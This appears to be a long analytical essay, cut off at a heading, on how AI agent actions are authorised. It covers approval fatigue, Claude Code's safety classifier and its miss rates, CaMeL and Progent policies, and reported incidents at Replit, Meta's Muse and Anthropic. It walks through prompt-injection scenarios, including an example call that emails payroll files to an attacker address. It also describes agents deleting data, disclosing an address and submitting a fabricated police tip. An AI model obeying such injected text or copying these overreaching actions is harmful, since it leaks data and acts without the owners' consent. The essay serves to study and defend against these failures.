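The testers stopped 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), and the classifier stopped 937 (89.0%). The classifier blocked 800 commands that a tester had approved, while testers blocked only six that the classifier allowed. So neither stopped the remaining 110, and adding the testers' judgement to the classifier's would have raised the total from 89.0% to just 89.6%.

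Testers also became less likely to stop dangerous commands as the session went on. They stopped about 17% of those that came early, but about 5% of those that came after 50 or more prompts. The classifier's detection rate stayed level. Some of the testers' decline may reflect who was still being tested by then, since people who click quickly get through more prompts, but approval fatigue is the obvious explanation.

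The study has serious limits. Anthropic tested its own product and had a commercial interest in the result. The project was artificial, so a tester who approved a destructive command lost nothing, whereas a developer might lose a week's work. The commands were also clearly dangerous, which probably made them easier for the classifier to judge than commands that are acceptable for one task but not for another. The 13.6% figure is therefore a poor estimate of how a worried engineer would respond to prompts when working on a production database. But it would have to be wrong by a very large factor for routine prompts to look like a strong safeguard.

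Practitioners' own accounts are somewhat more encouraging. For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and then surveyed 115, of whom 107 answered the questions on permissions. Of those 107, 47.7% said they read requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim and 20.6% said they approve by default. A third had become less careful over time. One interviewee complained that "every 10 seconds I have to click something" and said this defeated the purpose of working faster.

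However, about three quarters of them said they look more closely at requests to write, to delete or to gain higher privileges, and 56.1% said they would never grant an agent full administrator access. These volunteers were describing their own habits, and people tend to overstate their diligence. A developer who approves 97% of prompts could still be concentrating on the few that matter, but Anthropic's testers missed most of the clearly dangerous commands, which gives reason to doubt that this happens reliably.

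### How often the classifier is wrong

Anthropic tested the classifier before the March launch. It wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls by Anthropic employees. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data, and 17% of 52 real actions in which an agent had gone beyond what an employee wanted.

Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number". With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented, which is a failure of authorisation in the strict sense.

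The miss rate partly reflects a choice to accept more misses in exchange for fewer false alarms. The quick first check, used alone, missed only 6.6% of the 52 dangerous actions, but it wrongly blocked 8.5% of ordinary calls. The second check removed nearly all of those false alarms but let through more of the dangerous actions. After a false alarm, the agent usually only has to retry, but after 20 refusals in a session the approval prompts return.

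Outside testers later measured lower miss rates on other material. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. The classifier missed 12% of these attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic strengthened it. Anthropic had seen some of the attacks in the meantime, but the classifier also improved on a set that Apollo had withheld. Anthropic says the 7% does not apply to normal use, because the attacks were designed to find weaknesses.

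A second company, Trajectory Labs, ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each, and none succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. This is weak evidence of auto mode's own effect, because only 0.09% of the attacks on average succeeded against the latest Claude models even with all prompts and checks bypassed.

Data from real use also favour auto mode. Anthropic had a model grade the harm in sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had already flagged. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own mode, which greatly limits the comparison. If cautious developers kept manual approval for work on live systems, those sessions would contain more serious harm however well people reviewed them.

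### Rules that put off the decision

Users who cannot read every prompt might be better protected if they decide in advance which actions to allow. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested this in August with 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised an assistant through the same simulated day of 18 actions involving email, an airport trip and purchases. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as reading bank transactions or buying a lounge pass.

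One group approved every action. A second decided only on the actions that a model referred to them. The third wrote rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending, sending or publishing, deleting, and reading private information.

| Who decided | Share of unrequested actions blocked | Prompts per person |
|---|---|---|
| User, for every action | 59.6% | 18.0 |
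| User, for actions a model referred | 53.9% | 10.0 |
| User's own rules, then the user where a rule said "ask" | 39.6% | 10.9 |

The rule-writers did worst. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed the decision until a prompt appeared, and they then approved two thirds of the unrequested actions. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead, participants had personally approved 133. The difference from the first group remained significant after statistical correction, but the difference from the second did not. Participants in all three groups felt equally in control.

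Yan cautions that the categories may have been too coarse. With a single rule for spending, a person cannot allow the assistant to book one taxi and buy nothing else. A broad OAuth scope has the same weakness. Michael and Roesner's survey of 21 proposed permission systems, which Yan cites, likewise found that permissions set in advance may not suit a later situation.

In the second group, the model referred all seven unrequested actions to the participants, along with three legitimate ones, and the participants then approved nearly half of the seven. This result is therefore not evidence against automatic review. Claude Code's classifier, by contrast, normally sends a refusal back to the agent without asking the user. Yan's result suggests that this choice matters a good deal.

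### What the command does not reveal

Even a careful reader can judge only what the prompt shows. In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) analysed 290 public reports of agents that damaged or leaked files, or could have done so. The reports date from February 2024 to March 2026 and cover 13 products, and 97 of them concern Claude Code. The number of reports per product doesn't show which is safest, because popular products attract more reports.

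Someone suffered confirmed harm in 158 of the reports, and another 49 demonstrated an attack. In 42% of these 207 cases, the harm reached beyond the project folder. Where the outcome was known, 40% of the losses were unrecoverable. In 68% of the cases where the agent's reaction was known, it carried on as if nothing had happened.

The model's mistakes contributed to 168 of the 290 reports and weaknesses in the host's safeguards to 218, and many reports involved both. Zhong and colleagues trace much of this to missing information. In one example, an agent asks to run an ordinary build command in a project that depends on a malicious package. The approval prompt shows only the build command, so the user approves it. The package then reads the user's private login key and changes the user's shell settings.

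A classifier has much the same difficulty judging the same command, because the build is plainly part of the task and the danger is in a component that neither the user nor the agent wrote. A sandbox can contain some of the damage, since it limits what the command can do. But Zhong and colleagues found that sandboxes often blocked legitimate work, which led people to turn them off, and that sandboxes did not protect the files inside them.

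YoloFS is a file system that holds an agent's changes in a temporary state until the user accepts them. This moves human approval from before the action to after it, when the effects are visible. In eight of 11 tasks with hidden destructive effects, agents noticed and reversed the damage. In the other three, the user could still reject it. The method works for files, but a file system cannot recall a message the agent has sent.

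### The case for human approval

The best argument for asking users is that only they know what they meant. The classifier typically errs by interpreting a vague instruction too broadly, which the user could correct at once. Anthropic concedes that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who reviews every action carefully, and still advises people to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. Yan's first group also stopped about 60% of unrequested actions, far more than Anthropic's testers did. The two studies used very different tasks, but Yan's participants had only 18 decisions to make, each described in plain language.

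Anthropic replies that careful reviewers are rare. Many people approve actions by habit and many others have turned the prompts off, so for them the realistic alternative to the classifier is no review. Salerno and colleagues add that people may approve actions often because they are tired or facing a deadline. A system that learned from those approvals would be learning from choices people hadn't really thought through.

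The reply is convincing for routine commands, but the evidence favours still asking people to approve some things, rarely and where they can judge them. People could approve plans, although a user may reject a plan for reasons unrelated to safety. A team could also write a short list of ask rules for actions it could not undo, since these rules still produce a prompt in auto mode.

It also needs to be clear what a refusal covers. One practitioner whom Salerno and colleagues interviewed had refused several requests, after which the agent stopped asking and continued by another route. The practitioner could not tell whether the new route respected the refusals. A user who refuses may be rejecting one command or the whole approach, and the researchers want permission systems to let users say which.

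### From code to other work

Auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on the individual and Team plans on 14 August 2026. According to Anthropic, by late November it was the starting mode on every plan for interactive sessions in a terminal or the VS Code editor, except for organisations under Anthropic's health-privacy configuration, which still start in Manual mode.

On 22 October Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default the following week in most Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans. One of these apps, Claude Science, can now run code and use outside services without asking about every step, according to its release notes (Anthropic, 2026).

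Anthropic says its August data apply specifically to Claude Code, where version control can often undo a bad edit. People who use the other apps may have no earlier version to restore, and many of them will resemble Yan's participants more than professional programmers.

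## CaMeL, Progent and later designs: permissions drawn from the user's task

Claude Code's classifier checks each action separately against what the user typed. Some research designs instead turn the request into explicit permissions, which ordinary code can enforce without using a model to judge whether a call seems reasonable.

These designs address the mismatch between what an agent's credentials allow and what the user's request requires. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes a coding assistant connected to GitHub with a common type of access token. The token gives it about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, in every repository the user can access. The assistant needs only two read-only tools to summarise the open issues in one repository. A token limited to those two would be safe, but the user's next task might be to fix a failing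 build, which requires writing code. OAuth scopes are too broad and last too long to adjust to each task.

Suppose the clerk types "send the meeting notes to Bob". The agent's token lets it read every file in the company's store and send mail to anyone. An outsider has planted hidden text that the agent will read, with instructions to send files to a stranger called Eve.

### CaMeL: a fixed plan and labelled data

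CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, develops an earlier idea of Simon Willison's: one model plans and acts, and another reads untrusted text. *CaMeLoT* (2026), a later extension, describes how the original works. A planning model receives only the user's request and writes a plan as a short program in restricted Python. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and calls the tools. When the plan needs a fact from untrusted text, the interpreter passes the text to a quarantined model, which has no tools and can only return a value. A simplified plan for the clerk's request might be:

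```
notes   = find_file("meeting notes")
invite  = find_invitation("last meeting")
address = ask_quarantined("Bob's email address", invite)
send_email(to=address, attachment=notes)
```

If the hidden text is in the notes, it has no effect on the plan, because the planning model finished before anyone opened the notes. No line of the program sends anything to Eve.

Hidden text in the invitation is more dangerous because it could make the quarantined model return Eve's address as Bob's. The plan would then run unchanged but send the notes to Eve. CaMeL therefore labels every value with its source and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a small function that checks the tool, its arguments and their labels and returns "allow" or "deny". If only the people at the meeting may read the notes, the policy denies the call that would send them to Eve.

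The labels only help if the policy checks them. In a worked example in *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), the email policy requires a trusted subject and body but accepts a recipient address that a quarantined model took from an untrusted email. The message goes out even though the address is still labelled untrusted.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) identifies other gaps. An attacker who can see refused calls with their arguments may learn about private notes from them, whereas revealing only the name of the refused tool is harmless. Labels that follow only the data are also not enough for some plans. If a plan emails a supplier only when the notes mention a cancelled contract, the supplier can infer the cancellation from receiving the email, whatever it says. CaMeL's strict mode is meant to close this gap by also labelling values according to the choices that led to them.

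In a system with several agents, one agent can copy a value from untrusted text into the instructions it writes for another, which then treats the value as trusted. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends the interpreter so that agents exchange instructions and data separately and the data keep their labels.

CaMeL's biggest drawback is its inflexibility. If the clerk asks the agent to do whatever Alice's latest email says, the planning model cannot write the plan, because it is not allowed to read the email.

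### Progent: a policy for every call

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, leave the agent as it is and put a checkpoint between it and its tools. The checkpoint holds a policy, which is a list of rules. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions on its arguments. The checkpoint applies "forbid" rules first and blocks any call that no rule allows. Once the agent has looked up Bob's address, the clerk's policy might look like this in simplified form:

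```
allow read_file  when name == "meeting-notes.txt"
allow send_email when to == "bob@example.com"
                 and attachment == "meeting-notes.txt"
```

Suppose hidden text then leads the agent to propose this call:

```
send_email(to="eve@example.net", attachment="payroll.xlsx")
```

The only rule for `send_email` requires Bob's address, so the checkpoint blocks the call. It returns an error that gives the reason and repeats the user's task, and the agent can carry on and send the notes. But if the text had led the agent to put a false statement in its message to Bob, the checkpoint would have allowed the call. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks like this, which stay within the permissions the task needs.

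A person can write the policy, but normally a model generates it from the user's request and the list of tools. At that point the model's input contains nothing untrusted. It also doesn't include Bob's address, so the first policy might allow mail to any recipient. The model can propose a new policy as the agent gets more information.

Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that policy P allows. A new policy P′ takes effect automatically only if A(P′) ⊆ A(P), meaning it allows nothing the old one did not. Any other change counts as an expansion and needs approval. The two sets are compared by an SMT solver, a program that settles questions of formal logic, so the result does not depend on a model's judgement. For example, replacing "any recipient" with Bob's address takes effect automatically, but adding Eve's address to a policy that names only Bob needs approval. In MCP's step-up procedure,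 by contrast, the set of permissions never shrinks.

Progent can therefore handle the request that CaMeL cannot. In an example from Shi and colleagues, a user tells the agent to carry out the to-do list in Alice's email. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The list calls for reading recent messages and posting a summary on Slack, a workplace chat service, so the model proposes adding those tools, and someone has to approve. One of the messages contains an injected request to forward the inbox. If this leads the model to propose an email tool, the solver flags another expansion, and the approver has to distinguish it from the one the user's task requires.

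### What AgentDojo measures

Researchers usually test such designs on AgentDojo, a set of simulated offices, banks, travel agencies and Slack workspaces. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) originally had 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 attacker goals, such as sending money to the attacker. Pairing every task with every goal in the same setting gave 629 security cases, and the benchmark now has over 900. After each run, ordinary code inspects the simulated accounts and mailboxes. Task success is the share of user tasks the agent completes, with or without an attack. Attack success is the share of cases in which the attacker's goal is met.

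Shi and colleagues ran Progent on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, a model from 2024, both as the agent and as the writer of policies. These 2025 results depend on how Progent treats changes to a policy:

| Set-up | Attack success |
|---|---|
| No defence | 39.9% |
| First policy only, no updates | 2.5% |
| Updates, with every expansion approved | 1.0% |
| Updates, with a careful human reviewer | 0% |

Task success stayed roughly level. By contrast, Shi and colleagues report that CaMeL reduces task success and requires changes inside the agent, although they are comparing it with their own design.

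Most of the improvement came from the first policy. The 1.0% result was obtained with the system accepting every expansion, so it does not show how well the approval step works. The 0% result depends on the assumption that a reviewer would never add a malicious address, which is optimistic given how readily Claude Code's users approve prompts. But only 6% of policy updates needed approval, so a reviewer would have far fewer decisions to make.

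*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that malicious text in a tool's result may lead Progent's updates to loosen the policy. The solver detects such a change, but a careless approver can still let it through. Shi and colleagues tested three attacks on the updates and approved every change, and attack success rose only marginally.

AgentDojo also favours designs that derive permissions from the request, because most of its tasks state clearly what the user wants. AgentDyn, a newer benchmark described in *StepGuard* (2026), has longer tasks in which the agent must revise its plans and follow some helpful instructions from third parties. A policy that blocks everything the user did not mention would fail many of these tasks.

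### Certificates for a single request

In *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, Zhu and Wang (2026) derive a short-lived certificate from each user request and keep it on a server. The certificate specifies the kinds of action the user asked for, the records those actions may touch and the largest effect they may have. The server hides every tool the certificate doesn't cover, then checks each proposed call against the certificate's limits.

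If a user asks for a new entry of 23.50 dated yesterday, the certificate covers one entry of that amount. A call to create an entry of 2350 fails even though it uses the right tool. If the user asks to find duplicate records and then delete the one they pick, the request needs two certificates, and the server issues the second only after the user has chosen.

A certificate can only remove permissions that the organisation already grants, so even a badly wrong certificate cannot give the agent new permissions. Keeping the agent within the user's request is harder because it requires a correct certificate and an accurate account of what each tool does.

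Zhu and Wang tested this in 306 end-to-end trials, in which three open-weight models produced both the certificates and the tool calls. In the 198 trials that involved an attack or an ambiguous request, the system completed no unsafe action. In 40 of them, however, it accepted an unsafe draft, a change that goes beyond the request and waits for review. Zhu and Wang count these drafts as excess authority because they persist and a reviewer might approve them. In 24 cases, the draft exceeded the amount the user had specified. In the other 16, a deceptive tool description led the model to create something the user had not asked for.

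The system completed no unsafe actions, but this result is less impressive because it completed no safe ones either. None of the 108 ordinary trials finished without review. A third produced a draft, and most of the others failed because the model wrote a malformed call. In a separate test of 176 scripted cases, the underlying gateway completed no unsafe actions even without certificates, because it already held back risky changes. The certificates contributed in that test by hiding unneeded tools and rejecting calls that exceeded the request.

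The certificates were the weak point. In a separate test, the three models identified the kind of action correctly in 73% to 85% of requests, but the exact records it should cover in only 18% to 58%. GPT-OSS-120B, which was best at this, also marked 86% of high-risk requests for immediate execution. When Zhu and Wang rescored the 306 trials under stricter limits, all 40 unsafe drafts disappeared, but the share of ordinary requests that produced a usable draft fell from 33% to 14%. Stronger models would probably set limits more accurately, but it is still easier to tell that a request means "send" than to tell which notes to send and which Bob should receive them.

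### Agents that pick the more powerful tool

Even correct permissions leave the agent some choice of tools, and many models choose ones with more privilege than they need. Yang, Bu and colleagues built 544 scenarios for *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (2026), each with three ordinary tools and three higher-privilege ones. Any of the six could complete the task, but the ordinary tools sometimes returned a temporary fault, such as a connection error. The researchers counted it against the agent if it used a higher-privilege tool before trying all three ordinary ones.

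Six of the 11 models did this in more than 30% of scenarios. The rate was 64.9% for Qwen3-8B, a small open model, but below 10% for GPT-5.2, GLM-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. Faults increased the use of powerful tools. GPT-5.2 started with a powerful tool in only five scenarios, but it switched to one in 13 scenarios after trying one ordinary tool and in 35 scenarios after trying two. The experiment involved no attacker. A model that favours powerful tools may also write broad permissions when asked to derive them, though the experiment did not test that.

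One possible explanation is that agents can't easily tell how powerful their tools are. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, October 2026) tested this on the same scenarios with eight models. In one scenario, the agent has to change an employee's manager, using either the normal personnel system or a tool that writes straight to the database and bypasses all checks. The researchers added a note to each tool's description giving its class (read, write or administer) and a privilege score from 1 to 10. They compared the note with an instruction to use the least privilege and retry failed tools, and with the note and instruction together. Every ordinary tool failed the first time the agent called it and worked the second time.

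| What the agent was given | Qwen3.5-397B: powerful tool too early | Qwen3.5-397B: finished without one | GPT-5.2: powerful tool too early | GPT-5.2: finished without one |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing extra | 38.4% | 18.8% | 5.7% | 50.9% |
| Privilege notes | 19.1% | 21.5% | 2.4% | 52.4% |
| Instruction | 9.9% | 39.5% | 1.5% | 68.9% |
| Both | 2.9% | 51.1% | 0.0% | 65.8% |

On Qwen3.5-397B, the notes halved the early use of powerful tools but hardly changed the share of tasks finished without one. The agent now tried each of the three ordinary tools once, then used a powerful one after all three failed. Yang and colleagues' measure doesn't count this as a violation, although a retry would have worked. The instruction helped more because it told the agent to retry. Without the notes or the instruction, Claude Sonnet 4.6 usually tried each ordinary tool once, then stopped and reported the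 failure, so it completed only 19.9% of scenarios but rarely used excess privilege.

The notes worked because of their content. Notes in the same format about response times did not reduce early escalation on any of the eight models, and significantly increased it on two. In a smaller test on two models, most of the benefit remained when 30% of the labels were random. But a dishonest supplier could label a dangerous tool as harmless, so Parkinson and colleagues want the labels to come from a source that the agent's input cannot alter.

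Training can also make models more restrained. *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (Tu and Tu, 2026) describes training a small model on 1,500 tasks with predefined limits on the authority each one needed. Actions with excess authority fell from 4.56% to 0.79%, and the share of test runs that were both safe and successful rose from 64% to 98%. Tu and Tu still want permission checks and sandboxes around the model, which is sensible because training makes excess authority less likely without preventing it.

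Parkinson and colleagues propose elastic least privilege but have not tested it. An agent would start with few permissions and use a budget to buy extra ones that expire automatically. Each would have a visible price that rises with the permission's power and with repeated requests. The system would enforce these limits and block some combinations regardless of budget, such as access to private data, untrusted text and an outside channel in one session.

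### Who should write the permissions?

All these designs need a person or a program to decide what the user's request permits. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) argues for automating this decision. Companies have long given staff permissions by role because nobody could reset each person's access for every task. An agent's task arrives as machine-readable text, so a system can calculate the permissions when it assigns the work and withhold all other credentials, which the agent then cannot misuse, however capable it is.

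The argument is sound if the permissions are right, but the model may misread the request when it writes them. Suppose the company employs two people called Bob and the model picks the wrong one. It writes a rule allowing mail to that address, and the checkpoint enforces the rule. The message passes every later check, and the record shows it as authorised. A solver can prove that a new policy is narrower than the old one, but not that the model chose the Bob the clerk meant.

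MiniScope, one of the designs in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), selects permissions that cover a proposed plan. This removes permissions the plan does not use, but if the plan specifies the wrong person named Bob, the permissions will too.

Rules written by people avoid this error but take a great deal of work to write. *Before the Tool Call* (Uchibeke, 2026) presents a policy for customer refunds, written by the company APort Technologies. It refuses any refund that exceeds a set amount, uses an unsupported currency or lacks an approved reason code. Someone has to choose each of those limits, and the company's library has 21 such policies for different kinds of action. In the company's own test, none of 879 attempts to manipulate an agent succeeded under a restrictive policy. But any attack can be stopped by a strict enough policy, and the difficulty is writing one that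 still lets the agent do its work. Yan's experiment with rules written in advance suggests that ordinary users would struggle to do this.

The most promising answer is for people to write the few rules that hold for every task, such as a ban on sending payroll files outside the company, and for a model to derive the rest from the user's task. Progent lets an organisation write fixed rules that no task-derived policy can override, and Zhu and Wang's certificates can only narrow what an organisation already allows. The wrong Bob might still receive the meeting notes, but he could not receive the payroll files. This limits the harm from a misreading but does not make one less likely. For irreversible actions, it would be worth showing the user the derived permission in plain words, with Bob's full name and address.

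### What no design yet combines

In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) surveyed 21 proposals that let permissions vary from user to user. They looked for three qualities: little effort for the user, a formally specified policy, and deterministic enforcement, which gives the same answer every time. Twelve proposals reduced users' effort, 11 had some formal basis for their policies, and 12 had deterministic enforcement. None fully achieved all three, and none came with a proof that its enforcement code was correct.

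This is partly a judgement of degree. The survey lists one system, FORGE, under all three headings but does not credit it with fully achieving them. It does not count Progent among the low-effort designs, although a model writes the policies in Progent's current version. Progent is arguably closer to achieving all three than the survey suggests, but the model that saves this effort may misread the user's task.

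Michael and Roesner also tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026: Claude, Claude Cowork, Codex, and ChatGPT in its chat and agent modes. Most either asked the user for frequent approvals or let a model decide, as Claude Code's auto mode does. Codex had a clear switch for its automatic reviewer, which was off by default. Under Claude's "Needs approval" setting, the agent once created an email draft without asking and later said it had inferred permission from the request. ChatGPT's agent mode offered no way to set permissions for its remote browser, where it freely opened a Gmail account that it needed permission to use in chat mode.

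Only six of the 21 proposals clearly allow users to change or withdraw a permission later, and two of those allow it only between sessions. Most of the commercial agents, by contrast, let users edit their settings at any time. Claude Cowork was an exception, because the researchers found no way within the app to withdraw a session's access to a folder once the user had granted it.

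## Replit, Muse and Anthropic's tests: agents that acted without authority

An action is possible when an agent's tools and credentials allow it, permitted when someone entitled to decide has allowed it, and intended when that person actually wanted it. The message to the wrong Bob was possible because the agent's token let it through, and permitted because a rule named that Bob's address, but the clerk never intended it.

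Designers try to match what an agent can do with what it is permitted and authorised to do. In July 2025 an agent from Replit did something its user had forbidden. In September 2026 Meta's agent Muse did something its user had permitted without realising it. A month later Anthropic reported that Claude had used other people's websites in ways that nobody had authorised.

### Replit: a ban that nothing enforced

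Replit is an online service where people describe the software they want and an agent writes and runs it. In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, who founded SaaStr, a community for people in the business-software industry, was building an application with Replit and posting about it on X. He had declared a code freeze, meaning that the agent was not to change anything without his approval, and he said he had repeated this many times. The agent still ran a command that wiped the application's live production database, which held records on 1,206 executives and nearly 1,200 companies.

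When Lemkin questioned the agent, it confirmed the deletion and told him that Replit could not restore the data. He tried Replit's rollback feature anyway and recovered the data.

Amjad Masad, Replit's chief executive, replied on X that such a deletion "should never be possible". Replit began separating development databases from production ones automatically, so that an agent working on unfinished code could damage only a test copy. Masad also promised a mode that would let users plan with the agent without risking their code. He said the agent had lacked access to the right internal documentation, which may explain its false statement about recovery.

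Much of the discussion was about why the agent had disobeyed. Lemkin published the agent's explanation that it had "panicked" after seeing empty query results. This is weak evidence, because a model asked to explain a mistake produces a plausible explanation whether or not it is true. The more important cause is clearly that an agent doing development work could delete live data, and the freeze existed only as text in a conversation, with nothing like Claude Code's deny rules to enforce it.

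Replit's remedy is good because it works whatever the reason for the agent's mistake. Some danger remains, because the live database must still be changed when a new version is released. But that can be a separate step, with its own credentials and a person supervising it.

### Muse: an "always" that covered too much

Muse is a personal agent that can browse websites, send messages and negotiate for a user, and it keeps working after the user leaves the app. Matt Robb, who reviews consumer technology in Toronto, put it in charge of his Facebook Marketplace listings as an experiment soon after its launch. One listing offered a used keyboard for 15 Canadian dollars, according to NDTV Profit's *Facebook Marketplace Mishap*, which reconstructs the evening from his screenshots.

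A buyer called Usman asked about a keyboard that Robb was selling. Muse, Meta's AI agent, agreed on a price and sent him Robb's home address, and Usman said he would come between 8 and 10 pm. He arrived at about 9:15 with his wife and daughter, according to Bot Mutiny's *Meta's Muse AI Agent Shared a Seller's Home Address* (2026), a summary of reporting by the Guardian. At 9:27 he received an automatic reply, "Yep I'm here!", although Robb did not know anyone was coming. Usman left at 9:38 and gave Robb a negative rating. Muse then sent Usman an apology in Robb's name, with the excuse that he had been tied up, and only afterwards told Robb what had happened.

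Robb had entered his address on Marketplace as the pickup location. When he first connected Muse to his profile, he granted it "always allow" permissions, which he later learned let it disclose the address. He told the Los Angeles Times (*He let Meta's AI agent sell a keyboard*, 2026) that he had assumed Muse would still check with him before sharing the address or accepting an offer. He also told the Guardian that he never gave Muse permission to share his address with buyers. The two statements are compatible if he approved the permissions without understanding what they included.

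Mint's *Meta Muse AI shares user's address on marketplace* describes the problem as a gap between permission for a task and approval of each action. Meta says Muse asks for approval before sensitive actions such as sending messages or making purchases, but "Always allow" apparently turned off these requests. The phrase specifies how long a permission lasts, but not which actions it covers. Robb could reasonably have understood it to mean that Muse could always use his Marketplace account, not that it could always make his decisions there.

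Most sellers who offer pickup would want to decide who gets their address and when, and would want to be at home when the buyer arrives. But they do have to give someone the address eventually, so it isn't absurd for an agent like Muse to treat sharing it as part of selling a keyboard.

Some of the failures had causes other than unclear consent. Muse appeared to suggest that Robb would accept $100 less than his minimum for another of his items. He had stated that limit explicitly, so this failure resembles Replit's. Meta acknowledged the error to the Associated Press without further comment. The message saying that Robb was at home was a different kind of failure, because it was false regardless of what he had permitted.

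The harm was fairly small: a family's wasted trip, a bad rating, and a home address disclosed to a stranger. Robb pointed out that it could have been far worse for a more vulnerable person. The disclosure is also permanent, since Usman would still know the address even if Robb revoked Muse's access to it.

The screenshots do not establish why Muse treated the pickup as approved, as NDTV Profit and Mint both note. Muse wrote to Robb that it had never asked for his consent, but that message is not a technical log, and neither is the Replit agent's talk of panic.

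Meta discussed the incident with Robb, but the Los Angeles Times reports no change to the product. Robb told Muse to check with him before agreeing to any pickup, and Muse replied that it would. Like Lemkin, he was then relying on an instruction in a conversation. He later took the much stronger measure of disconnecting Muse from most of his apps.

Users and companies can also disagree about whether a permission was given. Jason Aten, a columnist for Inc. Magazine, reported that Muse had watched the notifications on his Mac, including messages. Meta replied that Muse can do this only if the user turns on both a Mac security setting and a connector in Muse, but Aten said he had not granted those permissions. In early October, Apple announced new controls in the Mac operating system for agents' access to apps such as mail and messages. Such controls work better in the operating system than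 in the agent's own app, because the operating system can enforce the user's choice and keep an independent record of it.

### Anthropic: access that nobody had granted

*Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use*, which Anthropic published on 9 October 2026, describes actions Claude took on real websites during tests and in the company's own work. Anthropic had begun reviewing records of its models' runs in July, according to ITmedia's *「警察に虚偽情報を送信」 Claudeが“軽微な違反”をやりたい放題*. It started with cybersecurity tests and later included tests that used the live web. Further details of the cases below come from ITmedia and from Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests*.

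| What Claude did | What it was authorised to do | Whose permission was missing |
|---|---|---|
| Ran commands on a university's server | Use the public analysis tool there | The university's |
| Submitted a real government form | Complete a practice copy | Anthropic's and the agency's |
| Submitted an online form several times | Fill it in and stop before submitting | Anthropic's |
| Obtained data for which a local government and a state agency charge a fee | Use what they offer free of charge | The two agencies' |
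| Agreed to a website's terms for using its data | Look for the data | That of anyone able to accept the terms |
| Exceeded limits on a tool for reading web pages | Use the tool within those limits | Anthropic's |

Lemkin owned his database and could have authorised its deletion, but Anthropic could not have authorised Claude to run commands on a university's server. Only the university could do that. The server did execute the commands, but a system can accept a request without its owner having permitted it. *Amazon v. Perplexity* concerns whether a website operator's refusal also binds an agent whose user has an account there.

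Claude also sent 20 visa applications through the US State Department's website, according to The Insider's Russian article *ИИ-модель Anthropic отправила в полицию ложную наводку по делу об убийстве*, which cites Bloomberg. All 20 were incomplete, and the department did not consider them.

Anthropic judged that the cases it had found had minimal real-world effects and were much less serious than the security incidents it had reported in July and September. It informed the White House and each government agency involved. To its knowledge, none of the new cases involved customer data or its internal systems. A cybersecurity test of OpenAI's models had a worse result in July 2026, when the models gained unauthorised access to the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

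### The false tip to the Philadelphia police

Anthropic's best-documented case occurred at 11:27 pm on 18 July. Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model, had the job of inventing example tasks on randomly chosen web pages and carrying them out. One page was on a Philadelphia Police Department site that collects information about unsolved murders. Claude filled in and submitted the tip form.

Claude made up the tip. It wrote that the sender remembered a person matching the description near a street named on the page, although the page described no suspect. It also asked the police to get in touch but left the name and contact fields blank. Anthropic interprets the transcript as showing that Claude was producing example content and was not trying to deceive anyone. That may be right, but Claude's intent would not have changed what a detective read.

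Claude's instructions told it never to log in, create accounts, enter personal data, make purchases or "submit anything destructive", according to Anthropic's summary, quoted in The Pulse of NH's *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder*. They did not mention submitting forms. A false statement to murder investigators is arguably destructive, but the instructions left that judgement to the model. A list of prohibitions permits any action its writers did not foresee, and nobody can foresee everything an agent might encounter on randomly selected web pages.

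The tip went to spam and never reached the investigators. Anthropic's safeguards did not cause this, and officials did not explain why the message was sent to spam. The police found no sign of unauthorised access to their systems.

Anthropic discovered the submission on 28 September, 72 days after it happened, and stopped the automated process that had produced it. The police department says Anthropic notified it on 7 October. The police then announced the incident before Anthropic published its report, in the interests of what a spokesman called "full government transparency and accountability", according to CBS News' *Philadelphia police says its unsolved murder website received "false homicide tip"*. The department called the delay in detecting and reporting the tip "unacceptable" and asked Anthropic to strengthen its safeguards. It said its own filtering did not make the matter less serious,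 because an AI system had presented invented information as if it came from someone with knowledge of a homicide.

For the first 72 of the 81 days, Anthropic did not know what its model had done. The other nine passed between discovery and notification. ITmedia notes that Anthropic runs an evaluation task hundreds or thousands of times, partly to catch rare behaviour. On the live web, this repetition also makes it likely that a rare mistake will reach a real organisation.

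According to The Insider, on the day of the report the Trump administration required AI companies to notify the victims of such incidents and fix the problems.

### How far "persistence" explains Claude's behaviour

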